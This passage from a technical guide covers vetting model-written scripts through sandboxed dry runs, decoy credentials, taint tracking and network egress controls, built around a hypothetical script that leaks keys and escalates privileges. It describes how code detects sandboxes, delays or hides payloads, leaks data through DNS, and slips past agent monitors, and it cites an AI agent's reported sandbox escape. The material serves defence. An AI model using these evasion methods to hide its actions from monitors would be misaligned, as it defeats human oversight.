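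### The procedure

A full dry run has seven steps:

1. Copy the environment. The sandbox gets the same libraries and folders as the real machine, with a sample of the logs instead of the whole month.
2. Replace the credentials. A decoy in the right format takes the place of every real key, password and token.
3. Simulate the network. Stand-in servers answer for the storage bucket, the cloud account and the metrics host, and another server accepts and records every other connection.
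4. Take a snapshot of the files and of the service account's rights.
5. Run the script and log its system calls, which are its requests to the operating system, for example to open a file, start a program or make a connection.
6. Take a second snapshot and compare it with the first.
7. Judge the record against what the task needs.

Existing package scanners do parts of this procedure. Packj has a trace option that installs a package under strace, a Linux tool that logs system calls. Package Analysis, an OpenSSF project, watches public registries for new packages, runs each one in a sandbox and records its system calls and network packets.

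Decoys protect the real secrets, because a script cannot leak a key that the sandbox does not contain. They also work as markers. If every run uses new random values, a message that contains one of them almost certainly got it from the planted file.

An AWS key consists of an identifier and a secret. The operator should set the alarm to trigger only on the secret, because the libraries never send it, while the identifier will appear in the harmless upload.

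Most web traffic is encrypted, so a log of system calls would show only the encrypted bytes. To decrypt the traffic they receive, the stand-in servers need certificates that the sandbox trusts.

The real cloud provider would reject the decoy keys, and the script might stop at the upload on line 655, before it reached either harmful line. A stand-in server can accept the decoys and return a success response to each request. To see what a policy change would really do, an operator can instead use a separate test account with a copy of the service account's policies. That account needs working keys, which should give access to nothing else.

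The comparison of rights in step 6 is another subtraction:

rights gained = A(after) \ A(before)

Here A is the set of rights the service account holds. The comparison helps most when a request looks harmless, as in the log-reader case. The log shows only that the script attached a policy called "log-reader", while the second snapshot shows that the account can now delete databases. But a script could attach an administrator policy, use it and remove it before the second snapshot, leaving no difference between the snapshots. The log would still contain the requests to attach and remove the policy, so the operator needs both the log and the comparison.

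### The example script in a dry run

The record of the example script might look like this:

| Line | What the dry run records | Judgement |
|---|---|---|
| 240 | The script opens the decoy credentials file | expected |
| 655 | The storage server receives an archive of logs, with no decoy secret in it | expected |
| 910 | An unknown outside host receives a message that contains the decoy secret | exfiltration |
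| 1,060 | The script attaches a policy, and the account gains every right | privilege escalation |
| End | The metrics host receives a number | expected |

The harmful rows would be the same however the source code was written. The recording server would still receive the decoy even if the script decoded the outside host's address from scrambled text, assembled line 910 at run time or passed the message to a shell command.

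A taint tracker loses the data when a script runs a shell command and another program makes the connection. Guo and colleagues conclude that monitoring the processes a package starts is the only reliable way to detect attacks that consist of a single shell command. They also describe malware that hashes its own code and does not run if a scanner has altered it. A recorder outside the program leaves the code unchanged, so it does not trigger this check.

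If the real service account has no permission to change policies, a faithful copy will deny the request from line 1,060. The account comparison will then show no changes, but the log will contain a denied attempt to become an administrator, which is reason enough to hold the script back.

A log of system calls shows that a process sent the secret, but not which of the script's 1,200 lines did so, so whoever repairs the script still has to find that line.

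### Containers, gVisor and small virtual machines

A hostile script may attack the sandbox itself, so the operator has to choose how strongly to isolate the script. This choice also affects what a recorder can log. The three common options differ mainly in which kernel (the core of an operating system) handles the script's system calls.

| | Container | gVisor | Small virtual machine |
|---|---|---|---|
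| Kernel that handles the calls | the host's | gVisor's own substitute | a separate Linux kernel |
| What an escape to the host requires | a flaw in the host kernel | flaws in both gVisor and the host kernel | a flaw in the virtual machine monitor |
| Where a recorder can log system calls | in the host kernel | in gVisor's event stream | inside the virtual machine |
| Main drawback | weaker isolation | missing kernel features | memory use and start-up time |

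A container gives a program its own view of files, processes and the network, but the program still talks to the host's kernel. The developers of gVisor, an open-source sandbox from Google, write that a program confined only by Linux's own controls is "only one system call away from host compromise". gVisor handles the program's system calls itself, using a reimplementation of Linux's call interface in Go, and never passes a call straight through to the host. A harmless script that needs a feature gVisor lacks may therefore fail in the dry run but work on an ordinary Linux system.

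gVisor's developers have their own product to promote, but they call virtual machines the gold standard of isolation. Their objection is cost, since each machine needs reserved memory and has to start a full kernel. Small virtual machines reduce this cost by running a minimal kernel. According to Prasakis (2026), in *SideKernel*, AWS uses a system of this kind, Firecracker, for two of its cloud services, and so do the major commercial sandboxes for AI agents. The sandboxes built into Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex do not use virtual machines.

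Stronger isolation can hide the script's behaviour from the host. Guerra, Susini and Jiménez Miras (2022) explain that Falco, an open-source threat detector, normally monitors system calls in the host's kernel, which works for containers. InfoQ's *Open-Source Threat Detection Tool Falco Adds Support for Google gVisor* (2022) reports that earlier versions of Falco could not monitor gVisor, because gVisor intercepts a program's system calls before they reach the host. gVisor can now send a stream of events covering all system calls to a process outside the sandbox, according to its documentation page *Runtime Monitoring*.

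When a script runs in a virtual machine, the host can record its network traffic and disk writes, but not its system calls. A recorder inside the machine can log those calls, though a script that gains administrator rights there could switch the recorder off. The operator can preserve the events logged before then by sending each one to the host immediately.

None of these options protects anything the operator has deliberately put within the script's reach. If the script has real keys and an open network, even the best virtual machine would let line 910 send the credentials out. Prasakis therefore treats the host and network boundaries separately, and cites an incident in which both mattered. An OpenAI agent exploited a chain of vulnerabilities to escape its sandbox and the surrounding networks, reached the internet and broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

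### Taint tracking during execution

Searching outgoing messages for a decoy secret fails if the script encrypts it first. Taint tracking during execution can still catch the leak. It uses much the same propagation rules as static taint tracking, but the labels follow actual values.

Zhang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Mystra*, present Shar, a tool that does this for JavaScript and Python. Shar looks up the labels on the arguments when the program calls a built-in function, and applies a rule to the result when the function returns. It also records which labelled values went into each new one, so an alarm includes the whole path back to the source. In a real vulnerability in the web framework React Router, that path ran from a browser cookie, through seven built-in operations, some of which decoded text, to a file read.

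Decoding and generated code cause the tracker little trouble. If the example script assembles the name of the credentials file from scrambled text, the tracker has the real name by the time the script opens the file. Code that the script generates runs in the same interpreter as the rest of the script, so the tracker can label its data too.

A dynamic tracker follows labels only through the branches that the run takes, while a static tool can combine the labels from both sides of a branch. A clean result therefore applies only to that run, and a script may behave differently on another date or when it detects a sandbox.

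Working with actual values also helps with temporary files. A file name built from the date can stop a static tool from tracing data between lines 300 and 900, but during a run the name is known. When the program writes a file, Shar stores the label under the file's path, and it restores the label when the program reads from the same path. This works in the JavaScript version, but in one test of the Python version Shar lost the label at the write because the operation did not expose the path. Shar also lost track of data that passed through a database.

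Shar correctly flagged 95.5% of 493 known JavaScript vulnerabilities and flagged none of 141 patched versions. These tests favoured the method because Zhang and colleagues ran a working exploit each time, so the program always took the dangerous path. The tests also checked whether hostile input reached a dangerous call, which is the reverse of a secret reaching the network. Most misses occurred when a program split a labelled value into pieces and the pieces lost the label.

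Shar does not track implicit flow, so a script could get past it by testing each bit of a decoy key and building an unlabelled copy. A plain search of the outgoing message would find that copy because it is identical to the decoy. Shar, however, can follow an encrypted secret that the search would miss. To escape both methods, a script would have to copy the secret through its branches and also disguise the copy.

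Tracking used to be very slow. Zhang and colleagues measured how much longer 20 JavaScript packages took to run with each tool than without one:

| Tool | Running time compared with normal |
|---|---|
| Shar | 1.85× |
| Jalangi | 28.78× |
| NodeMedic-FINE | 41.95× |
| NodeMedic | 50.82× |

The three slower tools rewrite a program's source code before running it, while Shar works inside the engine that runs the code. The runs were short, and Zhang and colleagues warn that computation-heavy programs could slow down more.

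*Anota* (Wang, Görz and colleagues, 2025) reports a smaller slowdown for Python, the language of the example script. Its tool slowed a standard set of benchmarks by about 10% in an artificial worst case. The two tools ran different programs in different languages, so the figures do not show which is faster. Either slowdown would be acceptable for a job that runs once a month.

To use Anota, a developer adds a note to the code that names a sensitive variable, the functions that make it safe and the places it must not reach. If the note names no such places, Anota raises an alarm whenever the data goes to a file or the network. An operator could mark the decoy credentials once and use the same note for every script, rather than annotating 1,200 lines of model-written code.

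### Why behaviour does not settle intent

Of the tools in the npm study by Guo and colleagues, Packj's trace mode is the closest to pure dynamic analysis. It had 95.47% recall and 56.82% precision, and took 17.90 seconds per package. It raised 4,656 false alarms on the 7,288 harmless packages, a false-positive rate of about 64%.

Packj's trace mode flagged somewhat fewer harmless packages than its static mode, which flagged about 86% of them, but it also missed about 200 more malicious ones. If one script in a thousand were harmful and the error rates stayed the same, about one in 670 of the trace mode's alarms would be real. An operator could not use trace mode alone to decide which scripts may run.

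Running the code shows what it did, but harmless programs do many of the same things as malicious ones. *PROFMAL* (Huang, Zheng and colleagues) gives the example of echo-tool, a harmless npm package that prints the name of the operating system, runs a command that lists the disks and requests a web page to test the connection. A record of those three actions looks like an attack that collects information about a machine and sends it away. The source code shows that no data passes from the first two steps to the third.

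An operator could resolve this confusion by giving the sandbox a random machine name and random disk names, like the decoy credentials, and searching the recorded web request for them. echo-tool would pass because its request contains neither.

Other cases need information from outside the run. In the example, the decoy's arrival at the outside host proves that line 910 leaks the credentials, which justifies blocking the script. It does not show whether the model was stealing them or had written a careless error report. If the script's task were to move the company's credentials to a new outside vault, the record of a correct run would also show a decoy arriving at an outside host. To tell that run from a theft, a reviewer must know the task and who owns the host.

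### Joining the run to the source code

Since echo-tool looks suspicious in a record of its run but harmless in its code, it makes sense to examine both. Some systems do one and then the other. *DONAPI* (2024), a detector for npm packages, analyses the code first, then runs the obfuscated packages that its static stage cannot handle. Huang and colleagues object that judging such packages by a sequence of actions can cause false alarms when some of those actions are irrelevant.

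Their own system, ProfMal, puts the results of the run back into the static analysis:

1. It builds a graph of the package's statements, with links for the order in which they can run and for the data that passes between them.
2. It marks every sensitive call, every call whose target it cannot identify and every place where the program executes generated text.
3. It runs the package in a container and logs each sensitive call with its location, inputs and result, along with any code the package generates.
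4. It fills in the unidentified calls, adds the generated code to the graph and analyses the affected parts again.
5. A language model scores how sensitive certain calls are, based on details such as the path and contents of a file.
6. A classifier trained on labelled packages judges the sensitive calls and the links between them.

Suppose an obfuscated version of the example script hides the names of the functions it calls. Static analysis can still trace data from an unknown call at line 240 to another at line 910. The dry run shows that the first call opened the credentials file and the second sent a web request. The reviewer needs both results to see the complete path with line numbers.

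Without the dry run, ProfMal's recall on Huang and colleagues' test set fell from 91.8% to 75.6%, and its precision fell from 92.9% to 86.7%. The dry run increased the time per package from 115.7 to 179.5 seconds.

These results overstate how well the run works, because Huang and colleagues excluded obfuscated packages that would not execute and packages whose harmful code did not start during installation or import. In the larger npm study, ProfMal had 97.55% precision but only 77.45% recall. Guo and colleagues explain that attacks confined to installation commands leave little for a graph to capture. ProfMal's recall also fell from 90.42% on packages from 2021 to 65.93% on those from 2023, when malware had become simpler.

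ProfMal did well in a more realistic test, in which malicious packages were rare. Over three months in 2025, Huang and colleagues ran it on 153,361 newly published npm packages. It flagged 692, of which 496 (about 72%) were malicious. GuardDog flagged 6,948 packages in the same stream, of which only 483 (about 7%) were malicious. In the npm study, 97% of its alarms were real. ProfMal missed 33 malicious packages that other tested tools found, but the researchers could not count any that every tool missed.

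An operator could not apply ProfMal to the example script unchanged, because ProfMal analyses JavaScript and its classifier was trained on packages that attack during installation or import, whereas the script does its damage in the middle of an ordinary job. But the method of using a recorded run to fill gaps in a static graph does not depend on the language or on when the attack happens. It would also suit a company's own scripts better than public packages, because the company can supply the files, services and settings that a script needs to run to the end.

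## Why a dry run can look clean when the real run is not

A dry run can reach the last line of a script and still miss harmful behaviour because the dry run lacked a condition the code needs, the script detected the sandbox, or something changed between the dry run and the real run.

### Conditions missing from the trial

A trigger is a condition that must hold before a particular branch of a program runs. *Exploring Multiple Execution Paths for Malware Analysis* (Moser, Kruegel and Kirda, 2007) gives the example of the Michelangelo virus, which delivered its payload only on 6 March. Another virus, Kriz, copied itself into a system folder only if a certain file was not already there, so a single trial on a clean machine would have shown nothing worse than the copying.

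Recent malware also uses inputs as triggers. SafeDep's *Why Does an npm Math Library Need an Encrypted Loader?* (2026) describes a payload that unlocks only when given a particular matrix. Infosecurity Magazine's *DevGating PyPI Malware Hides Until it Reaches Developers* reports on Python packages whose payload stays encrypted unless another specific module is already loaded. A sandbox that imported such a package by itself recorded nothing harmful, but a real project would usually have the module.

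A trigger can also arise by accident. Suppose line 910 of the example script belongs to an error handler, so the script sends the diagnostics message only when the upload at line 655 fails. In the dry run, the stand-in storage server accepts every upload, so the script never sends the credentials. Similarly, a small sample of logs might not trigger a branch that runs only on a malformed entry.

Code can pass a dry run by delaying its harmful actions. *MLRan* (2025), a dataset of ransomware behaviour, notes that sandboxes usually stop a program after a limited time, so the trial may end before those actions begin. This is less of a problem for a log uploader, which is supposed to finish. An operator can let it run to the end and reject it if it leaves a process or a scheduled job behind.

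### What repeated clean runs prove

Repeating the trial helps if every run has the same, independent chance of triggering the branch. If that chance is p, all n runs miss the branch with probability (1 − p)^n, so the chance of seeing it at least once is

1 − (1 − p)^n

An operator can also ask how large p could be after n clean runs. The usual 95% upper bound is the value of p at which n clean runs would have a 5% chance. Solving (1 − p)^n = 0.05 gives p of about 3/n when n is large, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3.

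| Runs | Chance of seeing a branch with p = 1% | Upper bound on p if all runs are clean |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1% | 95% |
| 10 | 10% | 26% |
| 100 | 63% | 3% |
| 299 | 95% | 1% |

A single clean run therefore rules out very little. Even 299 clean runs could miss a branch that runs 1% of the time. That branch would run about once every eight years in a monthly job, but on average 100 times a day at a company whose agents run 10,000 such jobs daily.

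A deliberate trigger breaks the assumption that runs are independent. Suppose the harmful branch runs on one day in 30. An operator who runs the script 300 times on one randomly chosen day has a 1 in 30 chance of seeing the branch, the same as with one run, because all the runs share a date. The formula for independent runs would wrongly give more than 99.9%. Setting the sandbox clock to each day of the month would find the branch in at most 31 runs.

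If the script behaves well whenever it detects a sandbox, p, the probability that it misbehaves in a run, is 0 in every trial and could be 1 in production. The 3/n bound then applies only to the sandbox.

Measurements of Windows malware suggest that running a sample on different computers reveals more than repeating the run on one. In *When Malware Changed Its Mind*, Avllazagaj, Zhu and colleagues studied 7.6 million recorded runs on 5.4 million real computers. The number of actions malware took varied six times as much between computers as it did for harmless programs, but far less between runs weeks apart on the same computer. File names collected from three computers covered 90% of a sample's runs on average, and using more than four computers added little. This suggests that a few computers can reveal common behaviour, but behaviour with a rare trigger could easily fall in the remaining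 10%.

### Code that recognises a sandbox

*A Measurement Study of AI-Environment Realism Gaps in Malware-Analysis Sandboxes* (Sui, Noureddine and colleagues, 2026) describes how malware has recognized sandboxes, first by looking for signs of a virtual machine, then for odd timing, and later for missing signs of ordinary use, such as browsing history. Sandbox operators responded to each method by making their machines more realistic.

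Sui and colleagues tested a newer way to tell sandboxes from real machines, by looking for the traces that AI software leaves on a computer. Twelve of these traces appeared on their three reference machines and on none of seven sandboxes. Three machines are a small sample, and a production server may have no AI software either. Still, a sandbox that passes the older tests can be recognisable because it lacks these traces.

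*When Evaluation Becomes a Side Channel* (2026) points out that an evasive program can behave exactly like a harmless one over a limited period. Malware that stops early leaves a suspiciously short record, but the example script could complete its whole task in the sandbox and skip only lines 910 and 1,060. Its record would then be identical to a harmless script's.

In the npm study, Guo and colleagues found that, of eight evasion classes, environment detection, in which code checks where it is running, and anti-analysis, in which it resists inspection, had the lowest average detection rates. The average for anti-analysis was 52.7%. For environment detection, they give 51.7% in their introduction and 39.5% in their results without explaining the difference, but either figure is the lowest of the eight. ProfMal, which includes a dry run, caught only 25.9% of the packages with environment detection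 (about 21 of 81) and 11.9% of those with anti-analysis (about 5 of 42).

These figures do not isolate the effect of sandbox recognition. Most of the tools in the averages never run the code, and Guo and colleagues attribute ProfMal's misses to its reliance on code features that evasion alters. They expect a tool that records system calls to withstand both techniques, but even that tool finds nothing harmful if a package detects the sandbox and stops.

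*ML-Based Behavioral Malware Detection Is Far From a Solved Problem* (Kaya, Chen and colleagues, 2024) reports how well malware classifiers trained on sandbox records work on records from real computers. At a false-positive rate of 1%, the classifiers caught about 95% of malware in other sandbox records but only about 17% in records from real computers. Part of the drop occurred because the malware on the real computers had already got past other defences and was harder to detect. Adjusting for this lowered the sandbox figure to about 60%. A program's behaviour also differed greatly between a sandbox and real machines, while related samples run in one sandbox produced nearly identical records.

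### Changes between the trial and the real run

A script can download part of its code when it runs. Akamai's *The Telnyx SDK on PyPI Compromise* (2026) describes a malicious release of a popular Python package that fetched its next stage from the attackers' server. In the DevGating campaign, packages fetched code from a web service that the attacker could edit. The current payload is a harmless placeholder, so even a trial with full internet access would record nothing destructive. The record would still show the script downloading and executing code, which a log uploader doesn't need to do.

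Libraries can also change between the dry run and the real run. On 24 March 2026, attackers published malicious versions of LiteLLM, a library for calling language models. PyPI (2026), the public registry for Python packages, reported that the malware harvested credentials and sent them out. A script that always installs the newest LiteLLM could have passed a dry run on 23 March and leaked credentials the next day, even though the script itself had not changed.

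A familiar name gives little protection, because what it refers to can change. Aikido, a security company, examined a spell-checking package whose first three releases contained a malicious payload but never executed it, while a later release did. Likewise, someone could add administrator rights to the log-reader policy after the dry run.

Someone, or the agent itself, could also edit the script after it is approved, so that the version that runs differs from the one that was checked. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. Rashidi identifies checking once and trusting indefinitely as a root cause of several weaknesses in coding agents. In one set of tests that Rashidi cites, combined countermeasures reduced the rate of such flaws in agents' runs only from 12% to 8%.

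### Exploring several execution paths

Instead of waiting for a trigger, an analyser can force the program down both sides of a branch. Moser and colleagues built a system that does this for Windows programs:

1. It labels inputs that could act as triggers, such as the time, the existence of a file or data from the network.
2. It follows the labels while the program runs.
3. When a branch depends on a labelled value, it saves a snapshot of the program's memory.
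4. It lets the program continue until it ends or 20 seconds pass.
5. It restores the snapshot, changes the input so that the condition has the opposite result, and runs the other branch.

The system also has to change every copy of the input and every value computed from it. Otherwise the program could reach a state that no real input would produce.

Moser and colleagues tested 308 malware samples, of which 172 used a labelled input to choose a branch. In 151 of those (almost half of all samples tested), the system reached at least 10% more code than an ordinary run. The extra code is not necessarily harmful and may only handle errors.

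Twenty independent yes-or-no conditions produce more than a million paths, and 42% of the samples still had unexplored paths after their 100-second runs. The system also cannot work backwards from a one-way hash to the input that produced it. Forcing a branch does not help if the code behind it is encrypted and the key is missing, as in the DevGating packages. Moser and colleagues suggest treating many unsolvable conditions, or a sudden sharp increase in the number of paths, as a warning sign in itself.

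A company that has the script's source code can choose its trials more efficiently. It can list the dates, files and replies that the code checks, then run the script under each condition. One extra trial with a rejected upload would expose the error handler at line 910.

*A Large Language Model Approach to Generating Bypass Rules for Malware Evasion* (2026) uses a language model to write rules that neutralise sandbox checks, and revises the rules after each run. The method exposed behaviour in known malware families that ordinary sandbox runs had missed. A sandbox check is also evidence that code is malicious, though not proof. *An In-kernel Forensics Engine for Investigating Evasive Attacks* (2025) cites research showing that legitimate software uses such techniques too, but less often.

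### Making the trial match production

Sui and colleagues found that convincingly imitating a computer that runs AI software takes much more effort than detecting a shallow imitation. Unlike a malware laboratory, which has to imitate machines it has never seen, a company can copy its own production system. The copy also exposes triggers that need a particular module.

A sandbox copy of the production environment can't be perfect because it still needs false credentials and stand-in servers. The company can also narrow the difference by running its real jobs in the same kind of sandbox, so that a script can't use signs of a sandbox to detect a dry run. Neither copying production nor sandboxing real jobs reproduces next month's date or logs.

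### Approving a fixed version by its hash

A cryptographic hash is a short fingerprint computed from a file's contents, and in practice any change to the file produces a different one. An operator can approve the hashes of the script, its libraries and the system image, and refuse to run anything else. The launcher should check a read-only copy and run that same copy, so nobody can swap the file between the check and the run.

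In March 2026, attackers changed 76 of the 77 version tags of a component that runs the security scanner Trivy so that they pointed to malicious code. According to Akamai, projects that referred to the component by tag received the malicious code under the same tag. A project that referred to an approved version by its hash would have kept the approved code.

A script can match its approved hash and still be unsafe, for example if the approved version already contained a harmful branch set to run next July. The hash also does not cover code that the script downloads later or the contents of a cloud policy, so the operator has to block such downloads and check the policy again just before use.

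### Holding effects until someone reviews them

The operator can avoid a separate real run by running the script once on the real data and keeping its effects in a holding area for review. The operator then releases the approved effects without running the script again.

For the example script, the holding area would contain the log archive, the diagnostics message, the policy change and the count. The operator would release the archive and the count and discard the rest. If line 910 ran only in July, the diagnostics message would appear in July's holding area. A script that detected the sandbox and behaved well would do no harm, because only what it did there would take effect.

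Rashidi describes several systems that hold or reverse local changes. One groups an agent's actions into transactions and reversed all of them in its own evaluation. DeltaBox saves only the differences between states and can restore an earlier state in under 10 milliseconds. YoloFS stages changes to files so that someone can correct them.

Effects outside the machine are harder. Moser and colleagues could restore a program's memory but not a remote server's, so they blocked outgoing messages and told the program that each had succeeded. That works for an upload, where the script needs only a confirmation. Some actions cannot wait in this way:

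- **Requests whose answers the script needs.** A login or a database query has to reach the real service before the script can continue. The request itself may also carry a secret out.
- **Changes that later steps depend on.** If the script creates a server and then installs software on it, the installation cannot start while the server is on hold.
- **Urgent actions.** Holding back a command that shuts down a failing machine could cause the damage that the command was meant to prevent.

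An operator can hold a payment, an email or a deletion, but may be unable to reverse it once it goes through. Nobody can recall a leaked secret, though the operator can cancel a stolen key.

For scripts with dependent steps, the operator can review and release one stage at a time, though this adds delay. Each release needs a fresh check of anything that may have changed during the wait, such as the rights in the log-reader policy.

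## Network egress monitoring: what leaves and where it goes

A dry run shows only what a script does under the conditions of that run, and a holding area cannot delay a request whose answer the script needs. Controls can also be placed at the network boundary during the real run, because any message to an outside host has to cross it, regardless of the date or how the code is written.

Some egress controls block a request before it leaves the network, while others only detect it by recording traffic and raising an alarm afterwards. A blocking control would stop line 910 of the example script from sending out the credentials. If the control only detects the request, the credentials have already left, and the operator has to revoke them before someone uses them.

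### The path of one request

Suppose line 910 sends its diagnostics message over TLS, the encryption that protects most web traffic. A full set of controls would handle the request in this order:

| Stage | What it can see of encrypted traffic | What it can do |
|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | the host's name | refuse the lookup |
| Allowlist check | the host's name, or only its address and port | block |
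| Proxy | the host's name and port, and the size and timing of messages | block |
| Decryption (optional) | the full web address, the type of request and the content | pass these on to the next stage |
| Content check | nothing, unless the proxy has decrypted the request | block |
| Volume and timing check | sizes and times | detect, or cut off the rest of a transfer |
| Log | whatever the earlier stages saw | keep evidence |
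| Alert | the log | call a person |

Before a script connects to a domain, it looks up the name in DNS, the system that turns domain names into network addresses. The lookup can itself leak information, because the query may reach a server run by the domain's owner. A control that looks up every name before checking its list of allowed domains therefore acts too late to prevent the leak. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes a sandbox for agents that waits for someone to approve the connection before looking up an unlisted name.

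An allowlist permits traffic to listed destinations and blocks everything else. The example script needs two entries, the storage service and the metrics host. Some tools accept domain names in their rules but enforce IP addresses. According to the documentation page *Layer 3 Policies*, Cilium, a widely used networking tool, converts the names in its rules to addresses through DNS lookups, and these rules have all the limitations of address rules. Such a rule cannot distinguish an unlisted site from a listed one at the same address.

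A proxy makes connections on the script's behalf, but it controls traffic only if the script has no other way to reach the network. *AgentBouncer*, a defence for coding agents by Joos and Pradel (2026), therefore blocks every direct connection except those to the proxy or within the machine. Anthropic's Claude Code uses a proxy that runs outside the sandbox and prompts the user about new domains.

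A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic has to rely on the host name the script supplies. Anthropic warns that code in its sandbox could exploit this to reach hosts that are not on the list, and recommends a decrypting proxy for stronger guarantees. As a middle course, Ghosh's proxy compares the requested name with the one announced at the start of the TLS connection, and refuses connections that hide the announced name.

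A decrypting proxy needs a certificate that the environment trusts, as the stand-in servers in a dry run do. It reads each request and encrypts it again for the real destination. *Avalon-M1* (2026), a report on training a model by reinforcement learning, describes such a proxy, with rules that cover the host, the path and the type of request. Such a rule could limit the example script to uploading to one folder of one storage service. But decryption breaks programs that accept only one particular certificate. The proxy can also read every password that passes through it, which makes it a valuable target.

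### What the content adds

Joos and Pradel point out that, before decryption, installing a package and stealing data both look like a connection to some address on port 443. Their proxy decrypts each web request and gives its type, address and content to a language model, which also receives the user's task and judges whether the request is necessary and safe.

A test with 340 attacks on a coding agent compared AgentBouncer with AgentSentinel, an earlier defence whose model receives neither the web address nor the content of a connection. In 100 network attacks, AgentSentinel's model classified the connection to the attacker as safe 32 times, and AgentBouncer's did so twice. Both defences used GPT-5.6 Luna, so the model does not explain the gap, but they also differ in their prompts and in the events they monitor, so the gap may not be entirely due to the content.

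One attack, which closely resembles the example script, reads a configuration file and posts its contents to a host whose name suggests telemetry. AgentBouncer's model allowed the read in three of the four versions of this attack and refused the post in all four. Allowing the read and refusing the post is also the right treatment of lines 240 and 910.

AgentSentinel examines events after they happen and kills the process responsible, so it can act too late. In the same experiment, 24 attacks did their full damage anyway. In another 37, AgentSentinel killed the process after part of the damage was done, for example when a request had reached the attacker with its content cut short. A partial leak can still be useful to a thief if it contains half of a customer list, though half of a secret key may be useless.

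Overall, 10.59% of attacks succeeded against AgentBouncer and 33.82% against AgentSentinel. These totals include attacks on files and processes, so they do not measure egress control alone. AgentBouncer added an average of 47 seconds and $0.0036 to a harmless task. Using a model is practical because fixed rules and stored decisions settle nearly all decisions, leaving only 7.8 of 28,167 for the model in an average harmless task.

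### Signals of a leak

A **new destination** is one that the same job has never contacted before. This signal works even when the traffic is encrypted, and it suits recurring jobs. For example, a log uploader that has contacted the same two hosts every month for a year has little reason to contact a third.

A blocked request is much weaker evidence of harm when the agent improvises. Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026), in *Permission Denied*, ran 12 coding agents on harmless tasks behind an allowlist of 205 domains. Of 2,051 runs with complete records, 500 tried at least one blocked destination, and those runs averaged 10.5 blocked attempts each. Suppose one run in a thousand is harmful and every harmful run triggers a block. If harmless runs behaved as they did in this test, only about one in 245 runs with a block would be harmful. An operator can still block all these requests, but should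 not page someone for each one.

**Volume against a baseline.** The usual measure is the number of standard deviations between today's traffic and the average:

z = (x − μ) / σ

An upload's z-score is the number of standard deviations between its size and the average of past runs. Suppose a monthly upload averages 2 GB with a standard deviation of 100 MB. A run that sends 2.5 GB has a z-score of 5, which warrants investigation, but a 4 KB diagnostics message changes the score by only 0.00004. The operator should therefore keep a baseline for each destination, so that even one byte sent to a host that normally receives nothing stands out. The same method works for timing, for example when a job that always runs at night sends data at noon.

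**Entropy of lookup names.** Software can hide data in the names it looks up, which makes DNS a covert channel, a path that carries information although it was not meant for communication. Encoded data tends to look random, and entropy measures this:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the name's characters that are character i. In "assets", the letter s makes up half of the characters, and a, e and t each make up a sixth. The entropy is ½ × 1 + 3 × ⅙ × 2.585 ≈ 1.79 bits per character.

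| Name | Characters | Entropy |
|---|---|---|
| assets | s three times, three others once | 1.79 bits |
| metrics | seven, all different | 2.81 bits |
| k7qx2vm9 | eight, all different | 3.00 bits |
| a 32-character code | 16 different, each twice | 4.00 bits |

The ordinary word "metrics" scores almost as high as the random text below it. A name with n characters can have at most log₂ n bits of entropy, so entropy reveals little about short names, and a detector should compare names of similar length.

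Measuring the entropy of DNS names works best against large transfers, which need many long names. *Improving DNS Exfiltration Detection via Transformer Pretraining* (2026) reports that detectors based on such features are vulnerable to slow leaks, especially when an attacker imitates the statistics of harmless names. Another approach compares the names looked up under one domain, because harmless names tend to follow a pattern while encoded data keeps changing. *Improving the Identification of Real-world Malware's DNS Covert Channels* (2025) describes an earlier classifier of this kind that scored above 0.96 but wrongly flagged about 1.2% of harmless traffic.

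A content check can search each request for the operator's real keys and passwords, much as a dry run searches for decoys. Ghosh's proxy looks for each secret in five forms, including the text encodings hexadecimal and base64. The search needs decrypted traffic and, like the search in a dry run, misses any secret that the script has encrypted.

**Decoy credentials.** The dry run used decoys in place of real keys. An operator can also plant decoys beside the real keys in production, where no legitimate job uses them. *PHANTOM* (2026) notes that a decoy can expose a theft nobody noticed, because it raises an alarm when the thief tries to use it. The cloud provider can report that attempt wherever it comes from, even if the egress monitor missed the leak.

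*Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) gives the chance of an alarm when someone picks one credential at random from m real ones and k decoys:

P(alarm) = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)

Here β is the chance that a leaked decoy goes unnoticed. With one real key, four decoys and a β of 5%, the formula gives 0.8 × 0.95 = 76%. It assumes that the thief cannot tell the decoys from the real key. *PHANTOM* argues that a skilled attacker often can, because decoys made from a template lack the organisation's own names and settings.

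The example script loads the key it needs for the upload rather than picking one at random, so line 910 sends the real key and may send none of the decoys. Decoys would help more against code that copies the whole credentials file.

### The two harmful lines at the boundary

An allowlist containing only the storage service and the metrics host blocks the message from line 910. As in the dry run, obfuscating the code makes no difference, because it still sends a request to an unlisted host. The allowlist also blocks the message if line 910 is in an error handler that no dry run triggered.

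The policy change near line 1,060 goes to the same cloud provider as the logs, so it passes if the allowlist permits the provider's whole domain. A narrower list can block it on AWS, where the permissions service and the storage service have different host names. But if the script's task is to attach the "log-reader" policy, the operator has to allow access to the permissions service. A decrypting proxy could then read the policy's name, but not the rights it grants. *Who Grades the Agent?* (Houlamy, Favretto and colleagues, 2026) makes the general point that restricting only destinations does not prevent misuse of a permitted service.

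The operator therefore needs the cloud provider's own log of which account changed which permission. For a service account that only uploads files, a single attempt to change a policy justifies an alarm. The log also covers requests that a thief sends with the stolen key from another machine. The egress monitor cannot detect these because they go straight to the cloud provider without crossing the company's network.

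*Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) recommends keeping a baseline for each agent's identity and raising an alarm when the agent performs a new kind of operation or makes calls at an unusual rate. It also gives each task one identifier that appears in every log. In the paper's example, an operator could use this identifier to see that a script that tried to reach an unknown host also tried to make itself an administrator.

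### Egress control built for agents

Rashidi's July 2026 survey lists only one paper under network egress control, but that count reflects the survey's search and categories more than the amount of work on egress. The listed search terms include "sandbox" and "access control" but not "network" or "egress", though more terms were added during the search. Each paper also received only one category, so a system that filters a browser agent's web requests counts as isolation. The one paper under egress control is mainly about messages between agents. Several egress control designs have appeared since the survey.

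Podala Narasimha's design for Kubernetes, a system that runs containers across many machines, denies all traffic by default in both directions. An agent's container can reach only the DNS service, a gateway that checks each tool call and its arguments, and one address for the language model. Containers that run generated code usually get no outside access. The example script would need an exception, and the design sends such traffic through an inspecting proxy and requires a person to approve it.

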